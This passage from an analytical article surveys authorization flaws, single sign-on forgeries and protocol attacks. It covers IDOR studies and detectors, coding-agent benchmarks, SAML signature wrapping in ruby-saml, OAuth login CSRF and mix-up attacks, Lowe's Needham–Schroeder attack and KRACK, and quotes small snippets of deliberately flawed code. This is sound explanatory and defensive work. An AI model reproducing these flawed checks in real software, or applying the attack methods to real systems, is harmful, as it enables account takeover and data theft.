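| Direct object reference: the attacker supplies a known or guessable identifier and reads the object | 31 (36.9%) | On Nextcloud, another person's username was enough to get their private out-of-office details, including a travel destination and phone number |
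| Tenant isolation: the attacker crosses from one organization to another | 7 (8.3%) | On HackerOne itself, supplying any organization's number gave access to its private bug reports |
| Workflow context: a check fails only when an object is in a certain state | 5 (6.0%) | At Shopify, staff could still see a customer's personal information after a removal that should have ended their access |
| Chained disclosure: one page reveals the identifier that the attacker needs for another | 4 (4.8%) | A US Department of Defense system revealed 2,000 document identifiers, and a second endpoint let the attacker download the files |
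| Object rebinding: the attacker alters the field that says who owns an object | 2 (2.4%) | In Cosmos, a blockchain system, an attacker could put a victim's address in the sender field and move the victim's funds |

The 41.7% figure covers only reports whose main family was an unauthorized change. Across all the reports, 39 (46.4%) let the attacker change, delete or trigger something, and 44 (52.4%) let the attacker read something. By either count, a tester who only tries to read Ben's invoice will miss a large share of these vulnerabilities. AuthProbe's cross-account test, as Barach describes it, covers only reads. The matrix should also include different roles, since in about 12% of Kaur's cases a user could reach an object belonging to someone with higher privileges, such as an administrator's external storage on Nextcloud.

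The exact percentages are less reliable. HackerOne's own programme supplied 13 of the 84 reports. If each programme has equal weight, direct object references are the most common category at 37.5%, and action-level cases fall to 32.4%. A language model did the initial classification, and when Kaur independently coded 20 reports, the two agreed on 17. Kaur also rated 21 of the 84 reports as low-confidence because they implied access to another user's data without demonstrating it. Choosing reports by upvotes probably also favours striking ones.

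Making identifiers hard to guess is a common but inadequate defence. In 31 of the 51 reports where Kaur could determine the format, the identifiers were ordinary sequential numbers. Some of the others only looked random. HackerOne and GitLab used identifiers that encoded a short text ending in a sequential number, so an attacker could decode one, add 1 and encode it again. A truly random identifier is harder to guess, but another page may reveal it. Kaur estimates that a tool that tried neighbouring numbers, with no understanding of the application, would detect roughly a fifth to a quarter of these vulnerabilities.

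### Inferring permissions from a database

Some specialised detectors try to work out the policy instead of asking for it. Huang, Shi and colleagues (2024), in *Detecting Broken Object-Level Authorization Vulnerabilities in Database-Backed Applications*, studied 101 real vulnerabilities and found that the rules they broke could be deduced from how the applications' database tables refer to one another. Their tool, BolaRay, infers four kinds of rule, which they illustrate with a discussion forum:

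- **Ownership:** Each post stores the number of one user, so only that user may delete it.
- **Membership:** A separate table lists which users belong to which forums, so only a forum's members may change its topic.
- **Hierarchy:** A notice belongs to a forum, so someone must be a member of that forum to manage the notice.
- **Status:** Each post is either open or closed, so nobody may comment on a closed one.

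This reasoning would produce both checks for the invoice page. A table linking users to organizations implies the membership check, and the organization number stored with each invoice implies the invoice check. BolaRay then searches the code for database operations that lack the necessary check. In 25 applications it found 193 real vulnerabilities, 178 of them new, and reported 54 false positives. *MOCGuard* (2025) describes a similar approach that uncovered 161 confirmed new vulnerabilities in Java applications. These results indicate that finding such faults did not always require a person to read the code, even before the language models of 2026.

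However, both tools assume that the structure of the data shows who may use it. A forum, for example, stores the author's user ID with every post, public or private, so the ID doesn't show who may read the post. *Rethinking Broken Object Level Authorization Attacks Under Zero Trust Principle* (2025) objects that people derived BolaRay's four rules from past cases, so an application with a different policy will cause false positives. BolaRay is also limited to PHP, according to Yang and colleagues.

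The rest of the application also provides clues to the policy. Yang and colleagues' detector, FLINT, compares each endpoint with others that handle the same type of object. In a plugin for Mattermost, a workplace messaging system, the endpoints for editing and deleting a comment checked that the user owned it, but the one for restoring a deleted comment didn't, which is good evidence of an oversight. The comparison wouldn't help if the programmers had forgotten the check everywhere.

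### Semgrep's 2025 test of coding agents

In a November 2025 article, Semgrep reported testing three coding agents, which are language models equipped to read and edit files. It gave them real open-source applications and a simple prompt asking for every IDOR. The agents found 15 previously unknown vulnerabilities and reported 93 false positives.

Claude Code, running Anthropic's Sonnet 4 model, did best, but only 13 of its 59 findings (22%) were real. OpenAI's Codex got 2 out of 44 with one model and none out of 5 with another. Semgrep then divided Claude Code's findings by where the application performed its access check:

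| Location of the check | Real findings | Share real |
|---|---|---|
| Nowhere | 11 of 16 | 68% |
| In one function or file | 3 of 6 | 50% |
| Spread over several files | 0 of 19 | 0% |
| Applied automatically by the framework | 0 of 18 | 0% |

(The rows add up to 14 real findings instead of 13, and Semgrep doesn't explain the difference.)

In a typical false positive, a page fetched a project by number with no visible access check, but the function it called, elsewhere in the code, verified that the user had access. Claude Code had apparently not followed the call that far.

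The fall from 68% to 0% is partly a result of how the categories are defined. If there is no check anywhere, a finding is wrong only if the owner meant the data to be open, whereas a page with a check in another file has a good chance of being safe. The table also gives only the share of findings that were real, not recall, which is the share of real vulnerabilities that the agent found. The prompt may have encouraged false positives too, because it told the agents that someone had already reported several IDORs in the code.

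Semgrep has a commercial interest in the result, since it sells a product that combines language models with its own analysis, and customers have less need of that if a general-purpose agent does well alone. Still, it published an example that reflects well on Claude Code. CVE-2025-59034 is a vulnerability in Indico, an application for managing conferences. Simplified, the code was:

```python
def export_user(self, user):
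    user = User.get(self._user_id)
    if not user.can_be_modified(user):
        raise HTTPAPIError('You do not have access', 403)
    return [UserSchema().dump(user)]
```

At first, `user` refers to the person making the request, but the next line reuses the name for the person whose details were requested. The permission check then tests whether that second person may modify their own account. This is always true, so anyone logged in could read anyone else's account information. A scanner that looked only for the presence of a permission check would miss this flaw.

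### Measurements with 2026 models

False positives were the main problem in 2025, but more recent models mostly err by missing real vulnerabilities. Semgrep's *We benchmarked A LOT of models, here’s how they compare to Mythos* (August 2026) compared models on 275 human-reviewed code locations, 144 of which were real insecure direct object references (IDORs). Claude Opus 5 found 38.2% of the IDORs, the most of any model without a specialised harness (software that chooses what code a model sees and guides it through the task), and 76.5% of its findings were real. Anthropic's Mythos found only 20 of the 144 (13.9%), and 80.0% of its findings were real.

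These numbers aren't directly comparable with those from 2025, because the test set and prompt were different. Semgrep could run Mythos only inside Anthropic's own security product, which searches for many kinds of vulnerability, and scored the results differently. The numbers also aren't very stable. The recall of another model, GPT-5.6 Sol, varied by a factor of 6.5 across three harnesses. Semgrep's *GLM-5.3 delivers Opus 4.8-level cybersecurity results at a fraction of the cost*, also from August, reports a recall of 58.8% for Opus 5 instead of 38.2%. Semgrep's own product reached 59.9% recall, but only 57.5% of its findings were real.

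In *Grounded or Gamed?* (2026), Semgrep ran five models five times each on the most difficult of its four codebases, which contained 27 real IDORs. Together, the models found 8. About half of the 19 they missed involved authorization spread across the code that a request passes through. The others were often simple. For example, the models found the missing ownership check when users downloaded files, but missed the same error when users requested documents or prompts. Semgrep suspects that the models had learned the textbook example, since tutorials on insecure file downloads are common. But the models didn't flag safe code that resembled a vulnerability, and they still made most of the same findings after Semgrep renamed the variables, so they weren't just matching familiar names.

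Much of the remaining difficulty seems to be in searching a large application. Duarte and colleagues asked an agent to audit whole repositories containing their 30 known vulnerabilities, and it found 3. It used an average of 59 of its 200 allowed turns, usually because it declared itself finished. Their system, ABSENTIA, found 19 when it listed every route and assigned an agent using the same model to each one. Each agent writes down a rule that its route should guarantee, such as "only the account that owns an invoice may read it", and then tries to construct a request that breaks the rule. A person still has a lot to review, because the system produced about 77 reports per application. A second model confirmed about half of them. A security researcher who checked a sample confirmed 42%.

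Yang and colleagues' results support the same conclusion. They tested agents on 69 pairs of vulnerable and repaired code, directing them to one endpoint at a time. Claude Code, running a DeepSeek model, flagged 91.9% of the vulnerable versions and 12.3% of the repaired ones. This is much better than any result in Semgrep's tests, but telling the agents where to look removed most of the search. The agents were also less accurate than the 91.9% figure suggests. Of 41 endpoints with vulnerabilities that Yang and colleagues had discovered themselves, Claude Code flagged 34 but identified the right operation in only 21.

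FLINT is designed to find access checks that look correct but aren't. A language model lists the operations that need protection and the checks that are supposed to protect them. A conventional program then traces whether each check applies to the user making the request and the object being accessed. In one business-intelligence platform, the code for deleting an access token (a password-like credential for programs) built a description of the token from the requester's own identity, then checked that description. Every requester therefore passed, much as in Indico, and could delete anyone's token by supplying its identifier.

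Yang and colleagues report 112 new vulnerabilities in 44 of the 57 applications they examined. In 41 cases the application checked the wrong object, and in 40 it had no check. They confirmed each vulnerability by running the application and carrying out the attack with two low-privilege accounts.

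## How single sign-on systems come to accept forged logins

The checks on the invoice page only work if the site knows that the person asking really is Alice. Many sites rely on another organization to confirm this, an arrangement called single sign-on. They offer a "Log in with Google" button, or send staff to their employer's login page, and accept the response that comes back. If a site accepts a forged response, it will give an attacker Alice's access even when its own access checks are correct.

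### A login, step by step

A login involves Alice, an identity provider that can check her password, and the service she wants to use. Many companies use a standard called SAML (Security Assertion Markup Language), which works as follows:

1. Alice opens the service, which doesn't yet know who she is.
2. The service sends her browser to the identity provider with a request for a login.
3. Alice logs in there, unless she has already done so.
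4. The identity provider writes an assertion, which is a short statement such as "this user is alice@acme.example". It signs the statement with its private key and gives it to her browser.
5. The browser passes the assertion to the service, which checks the signature and logs in whoever the assertion names.

Because the assertion travels through Alice's browser, she can edit it on the way. Encrypting the connection doesn't help, since she is at one end of it. Only the signature stops her from replacing her own name with her manager's.

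SAML uses XML, a text format that nests labelled elements inside one another. To sign an assertion, the identity provider first hashes it to get a digest. It then puts the digest inside a small block called SignedInfo and signs that block instead of the assertion itself. The service must therefore check both that the assertion hashes to the digest and that the signature matches the SignedInfo block containing that same digest.

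### Two parsers in ruby-saml

Services written in Ruby often check SAML logins with the open-source library ruby-saml. GitHub's *Sign in as anyone* describes two vulnerabilities in the library, CVE-2025-25291 and CVE-2025-25292, that let an attacker log in as any user of an affected organization.

The library read each document with two different parsers, which are programs that turn XML text into a structure other code can search. An attacker could write a document with two signature elements, arranged so that each parser found a different one. The library then assembled its two comparisons from these pieces:

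| Piece | Parser that read it | What it found in a forged document |
|---|---|---|
| Assertion | Nokogiri | "This user is the administrator", written by the attacker |
| Digest | REXML | The digest of that forged assertion, calculated by the attacker |
| SignedInfo block | Nokogiri | A genuine block from some other document |
| Signature | REXML | The identity provider's genuine signature on that block |

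The forged assertion passes the digest check because anyone can calculate a hash, and the SignedInfo block passes the signature check because the identity provider really did sign it. But the digest used in the first check isn't the one inside the signed block, so nothing connects the signature to the forged name.

The attacker needs only one genuine signature from the identity provider. Any user in the organization gets one by logging in, and GitHub says the signed configuration files that some providers publish can also work. A legitimate login contains a single signature that both parsers find, so normal use doesn't reveal the problem.

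GitHub's researchers found the vulnerability while deciding whether to use ruby-saml. GitHub had replaced the library with its own code in 2014 and was considering a return when another login bypass in ruby-saml, found by the bug bounty researcher ahacker1, became public in October 2024. *Unauthenticated SAML Login Bypass via Incorrect XPath* (ahacker1, 2024), reported to GitLab that August, appears to describe the same bypass, in which the library accepted digests from outside the SignedInfo block. GitHub then invited selected researchers to attack test systems that used ruby-saml, while its own Security Lab reviewed the code.

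Both ahacker1 and a GitHub researcher noticed the two parsers while reading the same function. At that point they only suspected a vulnerability. They still had to work out whether an attacker could use a disagreement between the parsers, find a document that caused one, and turn it into a complete login. ahacker1 did this first, on 4 November 2024, drawing partly on 2021 research into XML parsing. Eight days later the GitHub researcher had a second attack that defeated the planned fixes for the first. It used a different disagreement, which he had found with the help of ruzzy, a fuzzer for Ruby programs.

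The fuzzer was used here much as in the differential testing of certificate libraries, except that the two programs being compared were inside one library, and someone first had to notice that both were there. The security company PortSwigger reports in *SAML roulette* that it found the same vulnerabilities independently, so anyone who read the code closely could evidently have had the idea.

A fixed version of ruby-saml came out on 12 March 2025. GitHub points out that the library would have been safe from these attacks, even with two parsers, if it had taken the digest from the SignedInfo block it was already verifying.

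### Signature wrapping since 2012

The ruby-saml vulnerabilities are a variation on XML signature wrapping, an older attack that needs only one parser. The attacker keeps a genuine signed assertion in the document, perhaps moving it somewhere unusual, and adds a forged one. The code that checks the signature finds the genuine assertion by its identifier, but the code that logs the user in might take the first assertion in the document, which is the forgery.

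Somorovsky, Mayer and colleagues, in *On Breaking SAML* (2012), tested 14 SAML products and found 11 vulnerable to wrapping. Three, including two of the 11, could be made to accept an assertion with no valid signature. The wrapping flaws usually arose because one module checked the signature and another read the user's identity, but the first passed on only whether the signature was valid, not which part of the document it covered.

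A forged document must contain the genuine assertion, the forged one and the signature. To study the possible attacks systematically, Somorovsky and colleagues listed 24 ways of arranging these three elements side by side or inside one another. OpenSAML, a widely used library, resisted all of them. It compared the identifier of the signed assertion with that of the assertion it was about to use, and rejected documents in which two elements shared an identifier. However, the XML library that checked for duplicate identifiers didn't look inside certain elements, so an attacker could hide a duplicate there.

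Salesforce responded to the first report by accepting only messages with a single assertion. At the company's request, the researchers attacked the new version with handmade messages, found nothing, and at first considered it secure. A few months later they tried again with an automated tool built from their earlier results. The tool found a successful attack, which hid the genuine assertion inside an element that normally names the intended recipient. So even in 2012, a tool could find a logic flaw that experts had missed by hand, provided that someone had first programmed it with the structure of a forged login.

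The toolkits from the company OneLogin were vulnerable to every wrapping variant that the researchers demonstrated against products that sign only the assertion. The toolkits also accepted anything the identity provider had signed, including its published configuration file. OneLogin's name still appears in ruby-saml's code, and the 2025 attacks could use the same kind of file.

Only Microsoft SharePoint 2010 and SimpleSAMLphp withstood every test. Of these two, the researchers could read only SimpleSAMLphp's code. SimpleSAMLphp copies each assertion into a separate structure, verifies the signature there, and reads the user's identity only from that copy.

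Researchers have kept finding new attacks. Okta's *A Breakdown of the New SAML Authentication Bypass Vulnerability* (2018) discusses one that Kelby Ludwig of Duo Security had found in many implementations. PortSwigger's *The Fragile Lock*, which Zakhar Fedotkin presented in December 2025, returns to a patched version of ruby-saml. The patch had added two checks on the document's form but kept both parsers, and Fedotkin found other ways to make them read the same document differently.

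He also found an error similar to wolfSSL's empty digest. Before hashing an assertion, a library converts it to a standard form so that trivial differences in spacing or order don't change the digest. If this conversion failed, ruby-saml and several PHP libraries hashed an empty string instead, so the digest didn't depend on the user's name.

In May 2026 a wrapping flaw was found in authentik, an open-source identity provider that can also accept logins from other providers. According to GitLab's *CVE-2026-47201* (2026), anyone with an account at the other provider could reuse a valid signed assertion to log in as someone else. The same description would have fitted most of the products from 2012.

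Language models can now find such flaws too. According to Cyber Security News' *Claude AI Finds SAML Security Flaws*, a researcher at Oblique Security gave Claude Opus a description of what an attacker could do and had it explore SAML software. The model found complete login bypasses in four projects, three of them by signature wrapping. The researcher had it look for odd parser behaviour first and then try to build a working attack, much as the people studying ruby-saml had done. The article doesn't report how many leads failed to produce one.

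### OAuth and the "state" parameter

"Log in with Google" buttons generally use OAuth 2.0 or OpenID Connect, a login standard built on OAuth 2.0. OAuth was originally designed for authorization, such as letting a calendar app read Alice's appointments without learning her password, and websites adapted it for authentication.

In the most common form of OAuth login, the identity provider sends the user's browser back to the service with a short-lived code. The service contacts the provider directly to exchange the code for an access token, then uses the token to look up who the user is. OpenID Connect adds an ID token, a signed statement of the user's identity that serves the same purpose as a SAML assertion.

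The code is genuine, but it may have come from someone else's login. Suppose an attacker, Mallory, starts to log in with her own Google account and stops just before her browser delivers the code to the service. She then gets Alice to open the link containing the code, perhaps by hiding it in a web page. Alice's browser delivers Mallory's code, and the service may log Alice in to Mallory's account without Alice noticing. Security specialists call this attack login cross-site request forgery, or login CSRF.

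It's worse if Alice is already logged in and the service lets users attach extra login methods to an account. The service may then handle this as a request from Alice to add a Google account, and attach Mallory's. From then on, Mallory can log in to Alice's account with a click.

The `state` parameter exists to prevent this. When a login starts, the service generates a random value, stores it in a cookie in the user's browser, and sends a copy to the identity provider, which returns it with the code. The service continues only if the returned copy matches the cookie. Mallory's link carries the value from her own login, which matches no cookie in Alice's browser, so the service rejects it.

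Snyk's *1 Click, Zero Permission* (2026) describes how this protection disappeared from Langfuse, an open-source platform for monitoring applications built on language models. Langfuse handled logins with a library called NextAuth, which uses `state` by default. An optional setting let administrators choose different checks, and Langfuse passed it on in a line like this:

```js
checks: env.AUTH_GOOGLE_CHECKS
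```

If the administrator hadn't filled in the setting, its value was `undefined`, JavaScript's way of representing a missing value. NextAuth keeps its safe defaults if `checks` is absent. But here `checks` was present with the value `undefined`, and NextAuth copied that over the defaults, which switched off the `state` check.

Logins still worked normally, and the only visible sign was that the URL of the provider's login page no longer contained a `state` value, which few people would notice. The corrected code leaves out `checks` unless the administrator has set it.

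Snyk, which sells security tools, calls the result a total account takeover, but *CVE-2025-65107* (2025), an entry from Spain's national cybersecurity institute (INCIBE), rates the vulnerability medium, at 6.5 out of 10. The victim has to open a link while logged in, but that isn't much of an obstacle.

### Snyk's test of language models

In May 2026 Snyk tested whether Claude Opus 4.7 could rediscover the Langfuse flaw and three related ones in Python login libraries. Snyk's *How Cooked Are We?* (2026) describes four prompts, each more specific than the last:

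- Audit the whole codebase for vulnerabilities.
- Look for authentication vulnerabilities.
- Look for vulnerabilities in single sign-on and OAuth.
- Check that `state` is present, unpredictable and tied to the browser that started the login.

Snyk ran each prompt three times on each project, and the model had to find the flaw without any follow-up questions.

| Project | What was wrong with `state` | Least specific prompt that worked |
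|---|---|---|
| fastapi-sso | The library generated a value but never compared it with anything | Whole codebase |
| fastapi-users | The value contained nothing random, so Mallory's worked in Alice's browser | Authentication (2 of 3 runs) |
| Authlib | With one type of storage, the library didn't tie the value to a browser | The properties of `state` |
| Langfuse | The check was off by default | None |

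The model nearly found the Langfuse vulnerability without help. It reported that an administrator could turn the checks off, and described this as a dangerous option. When Snyk asked what happened by default, the model answered that NextAuth would use its own safe settings. It read the library's code and found the vulnerability only after Snyk quoted this answer back and asked whether it was sure. Langfuse's programmers had presumably made the same assumption about the blank setting.

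Snyk then added instructions to trace the consequences of every finding and have a second agent check it. With these instructions and the most specific prompt, the model found the Langfuse flaw unaided. But its report cited the later fix from the project's version history, so the model had access to the answer, though it also reproduced the error with a small script. The model also found the flaw with the original prompt when its reasoning effort was set to maximum. Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro found it in one of three runs.

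Another variation replaced the list of properties with a link to the OAuth security recommendations but still directed the model to `state`. The model found the same three flaws. For these libraries, a public document could replace an expert's explanation once someone had chosen where to look.

Snyk says, with good reason, that the test isn't a benchmark. It covers four flaws that Snyk already knew about, with no count of false positives. The published results for the authentication and OAuth prompts are identical, down to the average cost in cents, so one table may be a copying mistake. The people who asked the follow-up questions on Langfuse also knew that the model's answer was wrong. An auditor without that knowledge would have to question every plausible answer, which would take much longer.

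### The mix-up attack

The libraries in Snyk's test failed to do something that the OAuth standard calls for, but Fett, Küsters and Schmitz (2016), in *A Comprehensive Formal Security Analysis of OAuth 2.0*, found a flaw in the standard itself. They discovered four attacks while trying to prove the protocol secure, using a mathematical model of OAuth, browsers and web servers.

In the mix-up attack, Alice uses a shop that accepts logins from several identity providers. One provider, Honest, is trustworthy. Mallory runs another, Evil, and can also alter Alice's network traffic.

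1. Alice chooses to log in with Honest. Mallory changes the request on its way, so the shop records that she chose Evil.
2. The shop sends Alice's browser to Evil, which immediately redirects it to Honest.
3. Alice sees the login page she expected and enters her password. Honest sends her browser back to the shop with a code.
4. The shop has Evil on record as her provider, so it sends the code to Evil to exchange it for a token. Mallory can now use the code to impersonate Alice.

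Honest behaves correctly throughout, and the shop does what the standard required at the time. The response in step 3 contained nothing to show which provider had issued it. A shop with a single provider is safe from this attack but becomes vulnerable when it adds a second, even if the new code has no errors.

*OAuth 2.0 Authorization Server Issuer Identification* (Meyer zu Selhausen and Fett, 2022) prevents this attack by adding a parameter called `iss`, in which the provider puts its own web address. The shop compares this address with the one it has on record for the provider and stops if they differ. In the example, the shop would stop because it would receive Honest's address while expecting Evil's. Meyer zu Selhausen and Fett credit a 2015 paper by Mainka, Mladenov and Schwenk with first drawing attention to this type of attack.

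Fett and colleagues proved that OAuth with their fixes satisfies their definitions of security, assuming that developers follow the published recommendations. They noted that the proof doesn't automatically cover OpenID Connect, which adds its own details.

Software can still confuse one provider with another. In August 2026, INCIBE's *CVE-2026-73419* (2026) recorded a flaw in NextAuth, the library Langfuse used. Its `state` cookie wasn't tied to a particular provider, so a value from a login started with one provider could pass the check on a reply from another. Even a `state` value with all the properties in Snyk's prompt could therefore be inadequate.

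### Why the same faults recur

Some of these faults occur because developers misread the specification or didn't read it. The OAuth standard requires an unguessable value, but fastapi-users included nothing random in its value, and the documentation for fastapi-sso advised developers to use predictable ones.

The standard left out information that the shop needed, so closer reading wouldn't have prevented the mix-up attack. SAML has a less obvious gap. Somorovsky and colleagues noted that it doesn't specify the interface between the module that checks the signature and the one that reads the identity, so each programmer has to invent one. GitHub suggests that developers should probably disregard the SAML specifications because following them doesn't produce secure software.

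Disagreement between components accounts for more of the cases here than either of the other explanations. It covers the wrapping attacks and ruby-saml, and also Langfuse, where two pieces of software gave different meanings to a blank setting. (Published cases are a poor guide to how common each cause is, though, since Snyk went looking for errors in `state` and SAML researchers now know to look for wrapping.)

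SAML's more basic problem seems to be that the code that checks a document doesn't pass on the part it checked. Salesforce and ruby-saml both blocked a known attack but were then vulnerable to a new one, because their fixes still allowed the same document to be read in two ways. SimpleSAMLphp did better in the 2012 tests because it used only what it had verified.

Compatibility also makes these faults hard to remove. In November 2024, ahacker1 and the maintainer of ruby-saml considered dropping one of ruby-saml's two parsers, but existing applications depended on its behaviour, so the fix released in March 2025 kept both.

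## Attacks on cryptographic protocols before and after formal proof

The researchers who discovered the mix-up attack on OAuth were trying to prove OAuth secure. Others had been analysing cryptographic protocols this way since at least the 1990s. A cryptographic protocol is a fixed sequence of messages that uses encryption or signatures to achieve a goal, such as letting two computers confirm each other's identity. According to lecture slides from the University of Edinburgh, many exploitable errors come from the way protocols use sound primitives, the encryption and signature algorithms they rely on. A protocol can therefore fail even if nobody can break its encryption and every programmer implements it correctly.

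### The Needham–Schroeder protocol

In 1978, Roger Needham and Michael Schroeder published a public-key protocol meant to assure two network users, here Alice and Ben, that they are talking to each other. Each has a public key, which anyone can use to encrypt a message to them, and a secret key, which only they can use to decrypt it.

The full protocol has seven messages, but four of them only fetch public keys from a server. The other three use nonces, which are random numbers for use in a single run of the protocol. If *a* is Alice's nonce and *b* is Ben's, the messages are:

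```
1. Alice → Ben:   {a, "Alice"}  encrypted for Ben
2. Ben → Alice:   {a, b}        encrypted for Alice
3. Alice → Ben:   {b}           encrypted for Ben
```

Only Ben can decrypt the first message, so Alice concludes that he is there when *a* comes back. Ben concludes the same about Alice when *b* comes back, because only she can decrypt the second message.

Seventeen years later, Lowe (1995), in *An attack on the Needham-Schroeder public-key authentication protocol*, showed that Ben's conclusion can be wrong. The attack needs a third user, Mallory, who can intercept messages on the network and has a key pair of her own. It starts when Alice opens an ordinary conversation with her:

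1. Alice sends {*a*, "Alice"} encrypted for Mallory, who decrypts it and learns *a*.
2. Mallory poses as Alice and sends Ben {*a*, "Alice"} encrypted for Ben.
3. Ben replies with {*a*, *b*} encrypted for Alice. Mallory intercepts this but can't read it.
4. Mallory sends it to Alice unchanged, as if it were her own reply to step 1. Alice finds *a* inside, as she expected.
5. Alice returns {*b*} encrypted for Mallory, who decrypts it and learns *b*.
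6. Mallory sends Ben {*b*} encrypted for Ben.

Ben now believes he has a session with Alice, who has never tried to contact him. Mallory knows both nonces, so including them in later messages, as some people had suggested, would not prove who sent those messages. Lowe points out that if Ben is a bank, Mallory can pose as Alice and ask him to transfer £1,000 from Alice's account to Mallory's.

Nobody's encryption fails in this attack, and Alice and Ben follow the protocol exactly. The trouble is that the second message doesn't identify its author, so Alice decrypts Ben's nonce and hands it to Mallory. Lowe's correction adds one name:

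```
2. Ben → Alice:   {"Ben", a, b}  encrypted for Alice
```

In step 4, Alice would now find Ben's name where she expected Mallory's, and stop. The repair for OAuth's mix-up attack likewise adds the sender's identity. Martín Abadi and Needham himself had recommended in 1994 that a message include someone's name if their identity is essential to what the message means, and Lowe presented his correction as an instance of this principle.

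### What the model checker added

Lowe's first paper is three pages long and mentions no tool. It ends with a conjecture that the corrected protocol is safe. His second paper, *Breaking and Fixing the Needham-Schroeder Public-Key Protocol Using FDR*, describes using the program FDR to discover the attack, but notes that he had already reported it. *Formal Models and Techniques for Analyzing Security Protocols* (2017), a tutorial, credits the discovery to the second paper. Neither of Lowe's papers settles whether he first found the attack by hand, so the discovery is weak evidence for the effectiveness of either manual analysis or tools.

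FDR is a model checker, a program that explores every state a system can reach. It takes a description of the system and a specification, and checks that every trace (sequence of events) the system can produce is one the specification allows. Lowe described Alice, Ben and the most capable attacker he thought reasonable. The attacker could:

- overhear or intercept any message;
- decrypt messages encrypted with her own public key;
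- create messages from nonces she knew;
- replay any encrypted text she had seen, even without understanding it.

Lowe also had to define authentication. To authenticate Alice, he required that Ben commit to a session with her only after she had started a run with him. FDR found a trace that violates this requirement, the six-step attack above. It found no violation in the other direction, where Alice commits to a session with Ben. He reported that such tests typically took less than two minutes.

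FDR then found no attack on the corrected protocol, but it had checked a very small system in which Alice and Ben could each take part in one run. An attacker might conceivably learn something from a thousand runs that she couldn't learn from one. Lowe ruled this out with a proof by hand. In outline, the argument for Ben's side is:

1. To impersonate Alice, Mallory must return *b*, which Ben has encrypted for Alice.
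2. Mallory can't decrypt it, so she has to replay Ben's message to Alice in some other run and learn *b* from Alice's answer.
3. The message contains Ben's name, so Alice accepts it only in a run she believes is with Ben.
4. Alice has therefore started a run with Ben, and his belief that she did so is correct.

Lowe observed that this half of the argument doesn't need FDR. For the other half, he showed that any attack on a system of any size would also work on the small system FDR had already searched. He described the general method as proving what form an attack must take and leaving "the tedious checking of details" to the program.

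Lowe also noted that a 1989 paper that Needham co-wrote had included a proof of the original protocol, and he called that proof incorrect. Lowe acknowledged that his own proof assumes an attacker can't alter an encrypted message before replaying it. With cipher block chaining, a common way to encrypt messages longer than one block, the attacker can sometimes split the encryption of two items into separate encryptions of each, and the proof no longer holds.

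*Justifying a Dolev-Yao Model under Active Attacks* (Backes, Pfitzmann and Waidner, 2008) later gave a proof of the corrected protocol that applies to actual encryption algorithms, and described the previous proofs as resting on "unfounded abstractions from cryptography". In a Dolev–Yao model, like Lowe's, the attacker controls the network but can manipulate messages only by fixed rules.

### How a protocol verifier works

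Specialised programs for analysing protocols existed before Lowe used FDR. In *Analyzing the Needham-Schroeder Public Key Protocol*, Meadows compares FDR with one of them, the NRL Protocol Analyzer, and mentions others. More recent verifiers, such as ProVerif and Tamarin, can also analyse an unlimited number of protocol runs without a separate proof by hand.

ProVerif represents the protocol and the attacker as rules of the form "if the attacker can know this, she can also know that". Logicians call these Horn clauses. Slightly simplified, the rules for the original Needham–Schroeder protocol are:

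- **Alice starts:** The attacker can get {*a*, "Alice"} encrypted for anyone Alice chooses to contact.
- **Ben answers:** From {*x*, "Alice"} encrypted for Ben, the attacker can get {*x*, *b*} encrypted for Alice.
- **Alice finishes:** From {*a*, *y*} encrypted for Alice, the attacker can get {*y*} encrypted for the person Alice contacted.
- **Encryption:** The attacker can encrypt anything she knows for anyone.
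- **Decryption:** The attacker can decrypt anything encrypted for Mallory.

Alice and Ben have become rules that the attacker can use whenever she likes. Suppose the property to check is that the attacker never learns *b*. The tool combines rules whenever the result of one fits the condition of another, a procedure called resolution. If Alice contacts Mallory, the rules produce this chain:

{*a*, "Alice"} for Mallory → *a* → {*a*, "Alice"} for Ben → {*a*, *b*} for Alice → {*b*} for Mallory → *b*

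The property fails, and the chain is Lowe's attack. In the corrected protocol, Ben's answer contains his own name, but the rule for Alice's conversation with Mallory requires Mallory's name, so the chain breaks before the attacker learns *b*.

Cryptography is "perfect" in this model because the only rule for decryption requires the right secret key. There is no rule for guessing a key or exploiting a weakness in the algorithm. A user can add some weaknesses to the model, such as the message splitting that would invalidate Lowe's proof, but only if they have already thought of them.

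ProVerif's rules can be applied any number of times, so they cover any number of protocol runs. As a result, ProVerif can report an attack that would require a one-time step to happen twice. Tamarin tracks such steps more accurately. It searches backwards from a violation of the security property for a sequence of events that could have led to it.

No program can decide the security of every protocol when the number of runs is unlimited, as *Formal Models and Techniques for Analyzing Security Protocols* explains. A verifier may find an attack, prove that none exists in the model, or run indefinitely. If it keeps running, the user may have to simplify the model or supply an intermediate result to guide the search.

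### KRACK and the proof of the Wi-Fi handshake

A proof can remain correct after someone breaks the system it describes. When a phone joins a Wi-Fi network protected by WPA2, it exchanges four messages with the access point to agree on a fresh encryption key. In 2005 Changhua He and colleagues proved that this handshake keeps the key secret and authenticates both sides. In 2017 Mathy Vanhoef and Frank Piessens published KRACK, a key reinstallation attack on WPA2, which then protected most Wi-Fi networks.

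WPA2 numbers the packets that a phone sends and uses each number as a nonce when encrypting. The number must never repeat under the same key. KRACK makes it repeat:

1. The access point sends the third message of the handshake. The phone replies with the fourth, installs the key, and starts numbering its packets.
2. An attacker blocks the fourth message. The access point receives no reply, so it sends the third message again.
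3. The phone treats the repeated message as an instruction to install the key, and resets the packet number to its starting value.

The phone then encrypts new packets with numbers it has already used. In the usual WPA2 encryption method, the key and packet number determine a stream of bits, *s*, which the phone combines with the packet by an operation called exclusive or (⊕). If it encrypts packets *p*₁ and *p*₂ with the same stream, an eavesdropper can combine the results:

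(*p*₁ ⊕ *s*) ⊕ (*p*₂ ⊕ *s*) = *p*₁ ⊕ *p*₂

The stream cancels out. If the eavesdropper knows or can guess one packet, she can calculate the other.

The attacker never learns the key, and the phone and access point still identify each other correctly, so both properties proved in 2005 hold throughout the attack. The proof covered how the devices agree on a key, but not when a device installs that key, whether it may do so twice, or what happens to the packet numbers. The fix stops devices from reinstalling a key already in use. A verifier could have found the attack if someone had included key installation in the model and specified that packet numbers must not repeat.

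### TLS 1.3

The designers of TLS 1.3, the version of the web's encryption protocol completed in 2018, invited researchers to analyse it before it was final. Cas Cremers and colleagues modelled the tenth draft in Tamarin, along with a proposed feature that let a server request a user's certificate late in a connection. They found an attack while trying to prove that the combination was secure.

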